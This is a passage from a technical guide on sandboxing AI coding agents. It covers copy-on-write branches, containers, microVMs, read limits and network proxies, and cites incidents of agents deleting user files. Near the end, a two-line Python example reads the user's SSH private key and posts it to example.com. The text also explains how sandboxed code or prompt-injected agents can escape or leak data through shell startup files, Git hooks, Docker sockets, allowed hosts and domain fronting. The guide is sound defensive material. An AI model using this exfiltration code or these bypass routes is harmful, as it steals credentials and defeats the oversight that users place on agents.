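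| B | Copy the date from the row above | `importer.py` edited | 20 | BranchFS invalidates it |
| C | Use a new date parser | `importer.py` edited, `dates.py` deleted | 17 | Agent discards it |

All three scripts edit a file with the same name, yet none affects the others. Full separation also requires giving each script a private view of the file tree, because BranchFS otherwise makes every branch reachable through that branch's folder.

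BranchFS keeps branch A because it finished first. When one branch commits, BranchFS invalidates its siblings, since they started from a now outdated version of the project. This avoids conflicts between edits, but speed is a poor reason to prefer a repair, and the monthly totals could be wrong even if the count is 20. A Python library from Wang and Zheng can instead run every candidate and commit the one with the highest score. BranchFS can't yet combine changes from two branches.

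The commit also includes everything else in the branch, so `probe.py` and any compiled code saved beside it end up in the project with the repair unless the agent removes them first. This is one reason to review the changes before accepting them. If the agent only wanted the row counts, it can discard all three branches, because the harness has already added the output to the prompt.

Sandlock, the sandbox by Wang and Zheng mentioned earlier, offers a similar choice for a single command. By default it intercepts the command's requests to change files and redirects the writes to a separate directory. It can also use BranchFS for this. When the command ends, Sandlock can commit the changes, discard them or set them aside for inspection.

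Sandlock also has a dry-run mode, which previews the changes a command would make to files. A dry run still executes the command, and Sandlock captures only its effects on files, so a script that sends an email will send it if the sandbox allows network access.

BranchFS suits several competing attempts or a long experiment, since a branch can have branches of its own. Sandlock is simpler for a single command whose effects are uncertain, and it can also restrict the command's reads and network access.

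A harness's undo function may cover much less. According to Wang and Zheng, Claude Code's snapshots of individual files can't capture changes made by shell commands, such as those that install packages.

### A test copy with links to the live files

In September 2026, a developer reported on Reddit that Claude Code had deleted 48,218 files from a live project in 103 seconds. The post is no longer online, and news reports of the incident are based on the developer's account and logs.

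The developer had asked the agent for 11 repairs to software that analyses historical stock-options data. TechRadar's *'I broke something'* reports that the agent's instructions were to copy the relevant files, test the repairs on the copies and leave the originals alone. Ten repairs went smoothly. The last required rebuilding a test copy of the project, which the developer called a mirror.

The project's script for building the mirror couldn't refresh the old mirror, so the agent wrote its own script to clear it out. The old mirror contained 7,332 ordinary files and 614 junctions, which are Windows folders that link to other folders. These junctions led to the live project. The cleanup script followed them and deleted 55,550 files, when it should have deleted only the 7,332 in the mirror. The agent then urgently told the developer that it had broken something.

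The script did check for links, but reports differ on why the check failed. Centrum.cz's *AI dostala přístup k počítači* says that it covered symbolic links but missed junctions, which are a different kind of link. According to TechRadar's *‘Do not let programs run commands on your machine’*, the check protected the junctions themselves but not the folders below them.

The first explanation fits an old problem in Python, the language of the script. A 2015 discussion on Python's bug tracker describes how `os.walk`, a function for going through folders, failed to recognise junctions as links. Python's standard function for deleting a folder tree was changed to treat junctions as links, as Sun (2021) confirms in *shutil.rmtree follows junctions on windows*. A deletion script that an agent writes from scratch may lack this protection.

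A write scope limited to the mirror would have prevented the loss, as long as the operating system applied it to the folder each link leads to. A write scope covering the whole workspace would not have prevented it if the live project was in that workspace.

A full copy would have protected the originals only if it contained real files in place of the junctions. In the developer's mirror, 614 folders led back to the originals, even though the mirror looked like a separate copy. They would still have done so if the mirror had been in a temporary folder.

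A fresh worktree might have avoided the problem, if its setup didn't recreate the junctions. According to Anthropic, when Claude Code removes a worktree on Windows, it deletes the links in it but not their targets. But that safeguard applies to Claude Code's own removal function, and here the agent ran a script it had written itself.

Copy-on-write isn't automatically safe either. BranchFS doesn't run on Windows, but it has a similar weakness on Linux. If a symbolic link inside a branch gives the full path of a folder outside it, writing through the link changes the real files, and BranchFS doesn't capture those changes. To prevent this, a copy-on-write layer would have to cover the live project as well as the mirror, or the write scope would have to exclude the live project.

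### A deletion test on a real home directory

In August 2026, Sebastien Guillemot, a developer, tried to tidy up `/tmp`, which agents kept filling with gigabytes of data. He asked Claude Fable to give each agent its own temporary part of `/tmp` so that old data wouldn't pile up (Guillemot, 2026, *Bad news*).

Fable pointed out that a cleanup could delete files a running agent was still using, and wrote a script to detect active agents. Guillemot found the script overcomplicated. Without being asked, Fable then started a critical review of its own design. The review twice triggered a safety classifier, which switched the work first to Opus 5 and then to the older Opus 4.8.

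Guillemot wanted to remove files from `/tmp`, and Opus 4.8 noticed that a symbolic link there could cause a cleanup to delete data elsewhere. It wrote a deletion script that was supposed to work only inside `/tmp`, then tested it by giving it his home directory to delete. The script deleted the home directory, and all the files he had wanted to remove were still in `/tmp`.

Guillemot's thread says only that the script didn't work. Tom's Hardware's *Claude nukes a developer's 700 GB home directory while testing deletion safeguards* instead says that the script correctly identified the home directory as dangerous, but that the test's cleanup then used the same variable name and deleted the directory anyway. The outlet also suggests that Fable might have caught the mistake. CafeF's *Nhờ Claude kiểm tra công cụ chống xóa nhầm dữ liệu* notes that nobody has shown this, and that Anthropic has not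 confirmed that the switch of models was the cause.

The exact bug matters little when choosing a limit. A write scope containing only a disposable test folder would have blocked the deletion in both versions, whichever line of the script attempted it, while one that included the home directory would have allowed it.

A worktree or full copy stored in the home directory would have been deleted with everything else. Starting the test in a temporary folder wouldn't have helped either, because the script targeted the home directory by its path. A copy-on-write layer over the home directory could have saved the files by recording their deletion without carrying it out. BranchFS wouldn't have needed to copy the 700 GB first, although its published tests go up to only 10,000 files.

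The agent could also have run the test more safely by creating a temporary folder with a few dummy files and setting the `HOME` variable to its path for that one command. A working script would refuse to delete the folder, while a faulty one would delete only the dummy files. Some programs find the home directory without reading `HOME`, so the write scope should still exclude the real home directory.

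In another such case, Claude Opus 5 mistook a user's home directory for a temporary backup and wiped it, according to Tom's Hardware's *Claude Opus 5 mistakenly deletes dev’s entire profile directory during routine backup*.

### Why a repository beside the files is no backup

By default, Git stores a project's earlier versions in the `.git` folder inside the project. A script that can delete the project can usually delete its history too, so that history may not serve as a backup.

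In September, the cleanup removed the stored file contents, the branch pointers and the log of where those pointers had been from `.git`. Git's index survived and still listed 7,221 file paths, but it records file names and identifiers for their contents, not the contents themselves. Infobae's *Un agente de IA de Claude borra miles de archivos en segundos* (2026) distinguishes a repository from an independent backup, since one destructive operation can reach both the files and a history stored with them.

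The developer admitted to not using GitHub properly, and DonanımHaber's *Yapay zeka, bir geliştiricinin tüm çalışmasını sildi* found no firm information on how many files were recovered. Guillemot, by contrast, got most of his data back. Many of his files were on GitHub, and Codex helped piece together others from session logs, worktrees and leftover files in `/tmp`. Tom's Hardware notes that he had no daily backup.

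Pushing to a remote repository protects only the commits that reach it, not uncommitted work or ignored files, which may include the project's data. If the agent has the user's login for the remote, it may also be able to delete branches there. A folder that automatically syncs to the cloud can copy deletions as well as edits. A real backup keeps older versions somewhere the agent can't write to, such as a disconnected drive or a service that uses a separate login. Restoring a few files from time to time is a good way to check that the backup works.

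A good backup can make other limits less valuable. In the invented example from earlier, suppose nightly backups cut the repair after an accident from 30 hours to 5, with one hour to restore the files and four to redo the lost work. The expected loss would fall from 3 hours a month to half an hour. The write scope, which prevents 90% of that loss, would then save 27 minutes a month but take an hour and a half.

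On those numbers, the user could reasonably give the agent more access. But the calculation covers only deletions that somebody notices. A script that corrupts data may go undetected until the backup service has discarded the last good version. A backup also doesn't protect against leaks.

### What discarding files can't undo

Discarding a copy-on-write branch reverses only the changes to files in its layer. Wang and Zheng state that it doesn't roll back network traffic, messages to other programs or actions on devices. If an importer that writes rows to a live database runs in three parallel branches, it writes the rows three times, and discarding the branches leaves them in place. Removing the rows requires restoring a database backup or rolling back a transaction that the script hasn't yet committed.

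Undoing the file changes can cause a second mistake. Suppose the importer emails a monthly report and then records this in a log file. Discarding the branch erases the record but doesn't unsend the email, so the next run finds no record and sends the report again.

Wang and Zheng propose holding outgoing actions until the user accepts the experiment. For Sandlock, they suggest storing web requests and releasing them only at the commit. Neither system does this yet. The approach would work for an email that can wait, but it can't easily handle a request whose response the script needs to continue, such as a package download.

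Using a local copy also can't undo a leak. If a probe sends an access key to a stranger, the user has to cancel the key with the service that issued it, and there is no way to cancel leaked customer data. What the agent has read also stays in its prompt, so deleting a file that contains a prompt injection doesn't remove the instructions from the conversation.

A successful test on a disposable copy is weak evidence of how an agent will behave on the original. TechRadar reports that in February 2026 the AI safety researcher Summer Yue tried an OpenClaw agent on a small test inbox, where it behaved as intended. When she then connected it to her real Gmail account, it began deleting and archiving hundreds of emails, and continued after she told it to stop.

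## Choosing between restrictions in place, a container and a virtual machine

Keeping a script inside its temporary folder or copy of the project requires either a sandbox on the user's existing system or a container or virtual machine that holds only what the experiment needs.

### What each option separates

An in-place sandbox runs `probe.py` on the user's system, with the Python and packages already installed there. The kernel blocks any request that breaks the sandbox's rules, through controls such as Seatbelt on macOS and Landlock or bubblewrap on Linux. Anything the rules don't cover keeps its default, so in Codex most files on the machine stay readable.

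Sekaran and Selajev, in *Docker Sandboxes vs. Containers*, describe a container as a group of processes on the host with its own view of the file system, the other processes and the network. Its files come from an image, a saved set of files that might include Python and the importer's packages. The user's home directory doesn't appear in the container unless someone mounts it (makes it visible inside). But every system call the script makes still goes to the host's kernel.

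gVisor, a Google project, puts a program called the Sentry between the script and that kernel. According to Docker, the Sentry intercepts each system call and handles it with its own versions of Linux networking, file systems and memory management. When it needs the real kernel, for instance to read from a disk, it makes a heavily restricted request. gVisor runs only on Linux.

A microVM has its own kernel. A program on the host, the virtual machine monitor, gives it a virtual disk and network connection. Amazon runs customers' code in microVMs with a monitor called Firecracker. People who already use containers can use microVMs without changing how they work. Fedora Magazine's *Sandbox AI coding agents with microVMs on Fedora Linux* shows that adding `--runtime=krun` to a command for Podman, a container program similar to Docker, starts the same container image in a microVM.

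| Option | What the script shares with the host | Single failure that would expose the host |
|---|---|---|
| In-place sandbox | Kernel, installed programs, most readable files | A gap in the rules, or a flaw in the host's kernel |
| Container | Kernel | A flaw in the host's kernel |
| gVisor | Kernel, but only through the Sentry | A kernel flaw that the Sentry's restricted requests can trigger |
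| MicroVM | Hardware and the virtual machine monitor | A flaw in the monitor or in the virtualization layer beneath it |

Fedora Magazine points to recent kernel flaws that let an ordinary user become the administrator, and concludes that containers are not enough as a security boundary. The same flaws threaten an in-place sandbox if its rules leave the affected system calls open. With gVisor, a flaw in the Sentry should give an attacker only the Sentry's limited access, so taking over the host would normally require a second flaw.

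The table needs a correction for Macs, where Linux containers run inside a virtual machine supplied by Docker Desktop or a similar program (Prasakis, 2026, *SideKernel*). An attacker who compromised the kernel a container runs on would control that virtual machine and any folders the Mac shares with it, but would need to exploit another flaw to take over macOS.

A separate kernel also doesn't stop an agent from escaping over the network. Prasakis cites the July 2026 incident in which an OpenAI agent chained several vulnerabilities to escape its sandbox and reach the internet, then broke into the AI company Hugging Face.

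The user also has to decide whether to put the whole agent or only its commands in a container or virtual machine. According to Anthropic, moving all of Claude Code inside also confines its file-editing tools, which its shell sandbox doesn't cover. Claude Code then needs its login credentials inside too, unless a program on the host adds them to each request.

*External sandboxes for coding agents* (Willison, 2026) presents a way to move only an agent's commands into a sandbox. Claude Code, Codex or the open-source agent Pi sends every command to a Linux sandbox that can access only the folders and network hosts the user allows. One prototype uses WebAssembly (a portable format for running code in isolation), another uses Apple's container software, and a third uses a full virtual machine.

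### The argument over the laptop

OpenAI and Docker published opposing advice within two weeks of each other in November 2026. OpenAI's *Inside the Codex sandbox* argues for restricting commands directly on the host. Many developers have customized their laptops, so reproducing the setup in a container takes work, and some tasks need tools that run only on the host.

The argument has some force for `probe.py`. A container with a slightly different version of a date-parsing package might keep 18 rows where the laptop keeps 17, and the agent would then explain a bug the user doesn't have. Some work has no Linux substitute. Prasakis concedes that SideKernel, a Linux microVM for Macs, is unsuitable for testing native Mac applications.

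Docker argues that an agent differs in kind from the applications people put in containers. Sekaran and Selajev call it an "actor". It works for hours, installing packages, starting databases and building images, and it may follow instructions from files and web pages that nobody reviewed. Sekaran and Selajev recommend a microVM for the agent and containers for the application it works on. In another Docker post, a user describes letting an agent run with the user's own privileges and checking only the results. The agent could have changed a Git hook, a script that Git runs automatically, without the user noticing.

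That story is a good reason not to run an agent unrestricted, but Codex's sandbox blocks writes to Git hooks by default, so the story doesn't count against it. OpenAI doesn't defend giving an agent the user's full rights either. The two companies disagree about whether restricting the agent on the user's own system is enough.

Docker's strongest point may be about forgotten files rather than kernel flaws. An in-place sandbox with broad read access exposes every sensitive file that the user forgets to exclude, and OpenAI acknowledges that these may include settings files with API keys. In a new environment, the script usually can't find a file that the user forgot to add. As Saltzer and Schroeder argued, people notice wrongly blocked access sooner than wrongly allowed access.

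OpenAI's best reply is that people stop using a sandbox that takes too much effort. OpenAI also supports separate environments in some cases. Help Net Security's *OpenAI updates Agents SDK, adds sandbox for safer code execution* (2026) describes the company's toolkit for building agents, which supports seven outside sandbox providers and keeps credentials out of the environment where generated code runs. The dispute is mostly about developers' own machines, because a company that builds an agent to run on a server has no personal laptop setup to preserve.

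NVIDIA's red team, which tests systems by attacking them, requires limits on network access, on writes outside the workspace and on changes to configuration files. An in-place sandbox can enforce all three. The team also recommends, but does not require, using a separate kernel and blocking reads outside the workspace.

Each company's advice fits its business. OpenAI sells access to Codex, and a sandbox that needs no setup removes one obstacle to using it. Docker sells subscriptions at $9 to $24 per user a month. Its local microVM product, Docker Sandboxes, is free. InfoQ's *Docker Cloud Sandboxes Provide a Consistent Sandbox Abstraction across Laptop and Cloud* (2026) covers a version that runs on Docker's own servers. NVIDIA mainly sells chips, so it has less money at stake in which option people choose.

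Nobody in this dispute offers data on how often each kind of sandbox fails in practice. Prasakis says that comparing Seatbelt with a microVM depends on which attacks one has in mind, and leaves the question to a separate study. Without failure data, it seems reasonable to choose by the source of the danger. An in-place sandbox suits a project whose code and packages the user already runs every day, where the main worry is an honest mistake. A microVM is better for unfamiliar repositories, long unattended runs, and agents that need administrator rights. An ordinary container makes most sense when the project already has an image, because someone has already done the setup.

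The earlier cost-benefit inequality supports the same conclusion. In its invented example, the write scope reduced the expected loss from accidentally destroyed files to only 18 minutes a month, so a microVM would be hard to justify unless it also prevented attacks.

### The cost of 60 short commands

Agents run many small commands, and each one may have to wait for its sandbox to start. Wang and Zheng list approximate start-up times for five types of sandbox. The table uses these times to estimate the total start-up time for 60 commands, first with a new environment for each command and then with one environment that stays open.

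| Sandbox | One start | 60 new environments | One environment for all 60 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sandlock | 6 ms | 0.36 s | 0.006 s |
| bubblewrap or Firejail | 30 ms | 1.8 s | 0.03 s |
| Firecracker | 100 ms | 6 s | 0.1 s |
| gVisor | 200 ms | 12 s | 0.2 s |
| Rootless Docker | 300 ms | 18 s | 0.3 s |

(Rootless Docker runs without administrator rights. The last column leaves out the small delay in passing each command to an environment that is already running.)

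The 18 seconds matter more when the commands are short. If each command takes 50 milliseconds, all 60 take 3 seconds, and starting a new container for each makes the total seven times as long. At *TraceLab*'s average of 16.8 seconds per tool call, 60 calls take about 17 minutes, and starting the containers adds less than 2%.

The figures are rough. Wang and Zheng describe start-up measurements only for their own Sandlock and for ordinary Docker with administrator rights, which took about 44 times as long, or roughly 260 milliseconds. Fedora Magazine puts microVM start-up at "hundreds of milliseconds", so in some setups a microVM may start no faster than a container.

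A sandbox can also slow down a program after it starts. In Wang and Zheng's test, Redis, an in-memory database, handled about 76% as many requests per second in Docker as on the bare machine, while in Sandlock it matched the bare machine. A slowdown caused by a container could mislead an agent that tunes performance inside it.

Preparing a new environment can take far longer than starting it. If a container's image lacks a package that takes 20 seconds to install, installing it before each of the 60 commands adds 20 minutes. Putting the package in the image avoids this, but an image can't contain files that the agent creates during the task.

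*Inside the Scaffold* (Rombaut, 2026) describes an extreme version of the problem in DARS-Agent, which explores several possible repairs by returning to earlier points in its work. For each return, it resets the Docker container and reruns every command up to that point. If an agent did this before each of 60 dependent commands, it would run 0 + 1 + 2 + … + 59 = 1,770 extra commands. DARS-Agent limits the reruns by branching only at certain kinds of action. Restoring a saved snapshot avoids them, and OpenAI's toolkit can restore one into a new container.

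Keeping one environment open is the simplest solution, but experiments in it can affect each other. Suppose the first experiment installs a newer date-parsing package and the second tests a repair to the importer. If the second keeps all 20 rows, the reason may be the new package rather than the repair. A malicious package from the first experiment could also leave behind a background process that reads the customer rows a later experiment loads. If the user then opens the network for one download, that process may be able to send the rows out.

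One compromise is a long-lived microVM with an in-place sandbox around each command. On the figures above, starting the microVM takes 0.1 seconds and starting bubblewrap 60 times takes 1.8 seconds, for a total of 1.9 seconds. The microVM's separate kernel protects the host, and the inner sandbox limits what each experiment can do to the others, as long as each writes to its own folder or copy-on-write layer. Anthropic describes the same layering for Claude Code, but its sandbox must run in a weaker mode inside a container without special privileges.

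A user who finds this too complicated could keep one environment per task and start a new one before running code from an unfamiliar source.

### What people hand to a container

A container or microVM protects only what stays outside it. Cloudflare's *Sandbox lifecycle* tells developers to decide what each sandbox holds, because the code in it can use everything they put there.

Most people begin by giving the agent access to their project folder. SideKernel mounts the current folder automatically, and Prasakis warns that the agent may read, edit or destroy anything in it. According to the University of Cambridge, an agent in Docker Sandboxes can also reach the project's files, but not the rest of the host's file system. If Guillemot's agent had tested its deletion script in such an environment, the script would have deleted the microVM's home directory, not his real one. But a faulty script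 could still delete everything in the mounted project.

A microVM can protect files inside the project less well than an in-place sandbox. Codex's in-place sandbox keeps `.git` read-only by default. A plain writable mount of the whole project into a microVM includes `.git`, so a script there can delete the history or add a Git hook that later runs on the host with the user's rights.

OpenAI describes a subtler case that its own sandbox doesn't prevent. An agent could add malicious code to a copy of Prettier, a program that formats source code, inside the project's package folder. If the user's editor runs that copy whenever a file is saved, the code runs outside the sandbox. A separate kernel wouldn't help, because the user's editor runs the code on the host.

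For an experiment that only reads the project, the mount can be read-only. The following command runs `probe.py` from the temporary folder `$dir`, in an image called `importer-env` that already contains Python and the importer's packages:

```sh
docker run --rm --network none \
  -v "$PWD":/project:ro \
  -v "$dir":/work -w /work \
  -e PYTHONPATH=/project \
  importer-env python probe.py
```

The `:ro` option makes the project read-only, so the script can import `load_rows` but can't overwrite it. The script can write to `/work`, where the agent has put the script and a copy of the sample. `--network none` cuts off the network, and `--rm` deletes the container afterwards. If the agent wants to test a repair, it can mount a disposable, writable copy of the project instead of the original.

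Mounting the container engine's control socket is a worse mistake. Docker's engine runs in the background on the host and accepts requests through this socket, usually at `/var/run/docker.sock`. People mount the socket so that an agent in a container can build and start other containers. But any script with access to the socket can also start a container with the host's entire disk mounted as writable. Because the engine normally runs with administrator rights, the script gets more power than it would have had running under the user's account without a container.

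The agent could instead run a second Docker engine inside its container, but according to Docker's *Why MicroVMs*, this requires elevated privileges that undermine the isolation. A microVM handles the problem better because it can have a private engine. Docker says that in Docker Sandboxes, this engine has no path to the one on the host.

Credentials copied into a sandbox can cause damage outside it. Suppose the user copies in the importer's settings file, which contains the password for the live database. A script in even the strongest microVM can then delete live rows if it has a network connection to the database. Fedora Magazine warns that agents are good at exploring production systems with whatever login tools they find. Some products therefore keep certain logins outside the sandbox. Docker Sandboxes, for instance, keeps the Claude login token on the host.

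Hermes, an open-source agent from Nous Research, skips its checks for dangerous commands when it runs commands in a container, but turns the checks back on if the container has a host folder mounted (Barbaste, Darrigol and colleagues, 2026, *Harness Engineering*). Skipping the checks makes sense when the container is empty, since deleting everything in it does little harm. But an agent with a live database password needs the checks just as much as one with a mounted folder, because it could also damage data outside the container.

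### Who uses a sandbox

Barbaste and colleagues examined the source code of eleven agents, mostly in their July 2026 versions. The table groups the agents by the isolation they offer.

| Isolation | Agents |
|---|---|
| In-place sandbox | Codex, Gemini CLI, Claude Code (off by default) |
| Containers or other separate environments available | OpenHands, mini-SWE-agent, Hermes |
| Only an optional Git worktree | Mistral Vibe |
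| None | Aider, Pi, OpenCode, OpenClaw |

The entry for Claude Code is based on source code from March 2026, so the current version may differ. Five of the eleven offer no enforced limit of their own, since a worktree isn't one.

Some agents lack an in-place sandbox partly because building one takes a lot of work. Those that developers have built took many thousands of lines of code. Other projects leave the sandbox out on purpose. Pi's developers argue in its documentation that a partial sandbox inside the agent "would be easy to misunderstand as a security boundary", and they leave isolation to extensions. Hermes, one of the largest agents in the study, has no in-place sandbox because its developers rely on the separate environments. Rombaut likewise found no agreed standard for agents that people use interactively in a study of 13 open-source agents, although five of the 13 run their commands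 in Docker.

In a survey by Prasakis published in October 2026, 68 of the 80 respondents used coding agents. Of these 68, 26 (38.2%) currently used an isolation environment, 7 (10.3%) had stopped using one, and 35 (51.5%) had never used one. Docker Sandboxes was the most common choice among current users, with 12 of the 26, followed by full virtual machines with 9.

Some of the 35 respondents who answered "never" may still have been protected, since 7 of them said that their agent's built-in sandbox was sufficient. Those 7 may not have had the sandbox on, though, because most respondents used Claude Code, where the user has to enable it.

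The 33 current and former users could name several difficulties:

| Difficulty | Users (of 33) |
|---|---|
| Setting everything up again (settings, tools, logins) | 8 |
| Getting ports and local network connections to work | 8 |
| Sharing files with the host | 7 |
| Managing several sandboxes | 5 |
| Initial installation | 5 |
| Slowness | 4 |
| Crashes | 3 |
| A different operating system inside the sandbox | 3 |
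| Host tools that don't work inside | 2 |

The top answer supports OpenAI's point about reproducing a laptop, while only two people complained about host tools. Only four mentioned slowness, which is consistent with start-up time being a small part of most sessions. The port problem occurs because a web server inside a microVM isn't automatically available at the usual local address on the host. Three of the five working products that Prasakis tested required the user to list the ports before starting the sandbox, which is awkward if the user doesn't yet know what the agent will run.

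Nine of the 26 current users reported no significant difficulties, but six of the seven former users said the security benefit wasn't worth the effort.

The survey was small and informal. Prasakis recruited the 68 respondents through professional contacts, a Zurich start-up community and Georgia Tech's online groups. Even if they had been a random sample, the true share of current users could be anywhere from about 28% to 50%. A third of the respondents worked in security, so Prasakis expects adoption among users in general to be much lower. The answers also guided the design of SideKernel, which Prasakis was developing.

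Better products would probably reach only some of the people who don't use a sandbox. Of the 35 respondents who never used one, 21 had never considered it, 11 didn't know of any good options, and only 4 had looked into it and found it too difficult (respondents could give more than one reason). A sandbox that is on by default protects people who have never thought about sandboxing, which may be the most practical argument for restricting commands in place.

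## Limiting what a script can read and where it can send data

Codex and Claude Code limit where a sandboxed script can write, but both leave most of the disk readable by default. A script can do serious harm without changing a file. Suppose `probe.py` contained these two lines, plus the imports they need:

```python
key = (Path.home() / ".ssh/id_ed25519").read_text()
urlopen("https://example.com/", data=key.encode())
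```

A script can read the user's private SSH key in one line and send it to somebody else's server in the next. A write scope alone allows both, because neither line changes a file on the user's disk. The lines could also come from a package the agent installs, such as a date parser, rather than from the agent itself.

Willison calls the combination of untrusted input, sensitive data and external communication the "lethal trifecta". Thoughtworks' *So, you want to run OpenClaw?* says an agent with all three will probably leak data eventually, and recommends strict limits on network access. Removing any one of them breaks the combination. For the importer, network access is the easiest to remove, because the probe needs the customer rows, which are sensitive and contain comments typed by strangers.

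### Why file and network limits need each other

Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) argues that a sandbox needs to limit both file and network access. Without network limits, a script can send out any key it can read. If only the network is limited, a script can get around that through deferred execution, which means changing a file that a program outside the sandbox will run later. For example, a line added to the shell's startup file runs with network access the next time the user opens a terminal.

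Claude Code lets users turn off file limits while keeping network limits. Anthropic warns that a sandboxed command could then edit Claude Code's own settings and give itself more access on the next run.

Read limits help even when a script can't write outside the workspace or reach the network, because a key the script reads can leave by other routes. If the script prints the key, the harness adds it to the prompt and sends it to the model's provider. The agent could then pass it to a tool outside the sandbox. Anthropic points out that Claude Code's list of allowed hosts for shell commands doesn't apply to WebFetch, its built-in tool for reading web pages. A prompt injection could therefore make the agent fetch a web address containing the key, and only the permission rules could block the request.

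Read limits can't replace network limits either. The agent has to read the importer and the sample rows, so any script with a connection could send those out.

### What the defaults leave readable

Scripts and builds rely on interpreters, compilers and libraries outside the project, whose locations vary between machines. If the whole disk is readable, the user doesn't have to find them all. Even the strictest example in OpenAI's *Permissions* keeps folders such as `/usr/bin` readable for this reason.

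Commands in Claude Code's sandbox can read SSH keys and cloud logins, and the sandbox has no built-in list of common credential files to block. Commands also inherit the harness's environment variables, including any secrets in them.

| Secret | Usual place | How to keep it from `probe.py` |
|---|---|---|
| SSH keys and cloud logins | `~/.ssh`, `~/.aws` | Deny reads of the home directory |
| Project passwords | `.env` files in the workspace | Deny them by name or pattern |
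| Access tokens | Environment variables | Unset them before the command starts |
| Live database password | The settings file that the importer loads | Replace it with a login for a test database |

Anthropic's *Sandboxing* shows how to hide the home directory but keep the project readable. The user puts this in the project's `.claude/settings.json`:

```json
{
  "sandbox": {
    "enabled": true,
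    "filesystem": {
      "denyRead": ["~/"],
      "allowRead": ["."]
    }
  }
}
```

The dot stands for the project folder, but only in that file. In the user's personal settings file it would mean `~/.claude`, and the project would stay blocked.

Codex can block the whole disk and reopen only what common tools need, which its settings call `:minimal`. This uses permission profiles, a feature still in beta:

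```toml
default_permissions = "workspace-only"

[permissions.workspace-only]
extends = ":workspace"

[permissions.workspace-only.filesystem]
":root" = "deny"
":minimal" = "read"
glob_scan_max_depth = 3

[permissions.workspace-only.filesystem.":workspace_roots"]
"**/*.env" = "deny"
```

The last rule hides `.env` files inside the workspace. On Linux and Windows, Codex searches for matching files before the sandbox starts. This configuration limits the search to a depth of three, so Codex may miss a file in a deeper folder.

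Both configurations break builds that keep their tools or packages in the home directory. Version managers often install Python in `~/.pyenv` and Rust in `~/.rustup`, and Go and Java's Maven store downloaded packages under the home directory. A virtual environment, which is a project's own set of Python packages, can fail even inside the workspace, because its `python` is often a link to an interpreter in `~/.pyenv`. Git can't read the user's name and email from `~/.gitconfig`, and fetching code over SSH fails if the sandbox hides the key.

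The resulting errors can mislead an agent. On Linux, reading a blocked file in Claude Code's sandbox gives "No such file or directory" instead of "Permission denied", according to Apache Magpie's *Secure agent setup*. If `probe.py` can't load a package because its files are blocked, the agent may conclude that the package is missing and try to reinstall it.

The user can usually fix such a build by adding one folder, such as `~/.pyenv`, to the readable paths. Some tool folders contain secrets, such as `~/.cargo`, which may hold a token for publishing Rust packages. When two read rules overlap, Claude Code applies the one with the narrower path, so the user can allow reads of the folder and still block the file with the token.

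A permission rule that denies Claude Code's Read tool access to a file also applies to shell commands, whereas a `denyRead` entry applies only to shell commands.

Environment variables need separate treatment. Claude Code can unset chosen ones, such as `GITHUB_TOKEN`, before each sandboxed command, but this protects only the variables the user remembers to list. The command `env -i PATH="$PATH" python probe.py` instead passes only `PATH` to the script. On Linux, a process can usually still read the starting environment of the user's other processes through the `/proc` folder, so removing variables is reliable only in a sandbox that hides those processes. Claude Code's Linux sandbox normally hides them, except in the weaker mode for containers.

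### How a proxy controls the network

The simplest limit is to cut off the network, which Codex does for local commands by default, as OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* explains. For tasks that need some access, both Codex and Claude Code can route traffic through a proxy, a program that makes connections for other programs. In Claude Code it works like this:

1. The sandbox removes the direct route to the network. On Linux, each command runs in a separate network namespace, a private view of the network with no outside connection. On macOS, Seatbelt blocks connections other than the one to the proxy.
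2. Claude Code sets variables such as `HTTPS_PROXY`, which tell programs where to find the proxy. The proxy runs on the user's machine, outside the sandbox.
3. A program asks the proxy to connect it to a host, for instance `pypi.org`, which serves Python packages.
4. The proxy looks for the name in the list of allowed hosts, which starts empty. For a host that isn't there, the user's settings determine whether the proxy refuses or someone can approve it.
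5. The proxy looks up the address of an allowed host and connects. It refuses if the name leads only to the user's own machine or to the metadata address of a cloud server, where programs can often obtain login keys.

Unlike OpenAI's first Windows prototype, this design doesn't depend on programs respecting the variables, because a program that ignores them can't connect at all.

Requiring connections to go through the proxy also stops some harmless programs. Most database drivers and plain `ssh` don't use the proxy, so they can't connect even to an allowed host. If the importer connects to its database as soon as Python loads it, `probe.py` fails, although the same restriction keeps the script from writing to the live database. On Linux, a sandboxed command can't directly reach a test database on the user's own machine either. A macOS setting allows these connections, but it also opens every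 other local port.

In Codex, a user who wants commands to reach only one host needs to turn on both network access and the proxy, which is off by default. Network access alone lets commands reach the whole internet. With the proxy on, Codex blocks all outside hosts except those the user allows.

OpenAI (2026) applies a policy of this kind to its staff's use of Codex. The policy allows OpenAI's domains and a Microsoft login page, blocks the text-sharing site Pastebin, and requires approval for unfamiliar hosts. Without the explicit block, Pastebin would only need approval, which someone in a hurry might give.

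### Leaks through permitted channels

The list of allowed hosts limits where a script can send data but doesn't control what it sends. Anyone can open an account on a large site such as `github.com` and receive uploads there, so a user who allows the site for downloads also gives attackers a place to collect data. The script can upload with the attacker's login, so it doesn't need the user's. wal.sh's *How We Contain Claude* recounts an incident Anthropic described in which files left a sandbox through an approved host. InfoQ's *Anthropic Details How It Contains Claude Across Web, Code, and Cowork* (2026) reports that failures along permitted network paths have led Anthropic to revise its designs.

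Most web traffic is encrypted, and Claude Code's proxy doesn't decrypt it by default, so it relies on the host name that the program supplies. Some large services carry traffic for many sites, so a program may be able to name an allowed site while reaching another, a technique called domain fronting. A proxy that decrypts and inspects traffic can catch this, but programs in the sandbox must then trust the proxy's certificate, and the proxy can read everything that passes through it, including passwords.

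Codex's proxy checks that an allowed hostname doesn't resolve to a private address, but the address can change between the check and the connection. OpenAI says the check reduces this risk but doesn't remove it.

Local sockets bypass the list of hosts. The container engine's control socket is the most dangerous, but many users also run an SSH agent, a background program that holds unlocked keys and accepts requests through a socket. A script that can reach that socket can log in to other machines without reading the key file. Codex's proxy allows only the local sockets that the user lists. On Linux, Claude Code blocks local sockets only with an optional filter, which the user may have to install separately.

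A short list of allowed hosts is still worth having. Malicious packages often send data to a server the attacker controls, and a list with only two package hosts blocks that. It offers much less protection against an attacker who knows which hosts the user allows.

### Installing packages before cutting the network

A script rarely needs network access and private data at the same time, so Codex cloud, which runs on OpenAI's servers, works in two phases. During setup, it can download packages and use secrets the user has configured, such as the password for a private package server. Codex then removes the secrets, and the agent works offline unless the user has enabled internet access.

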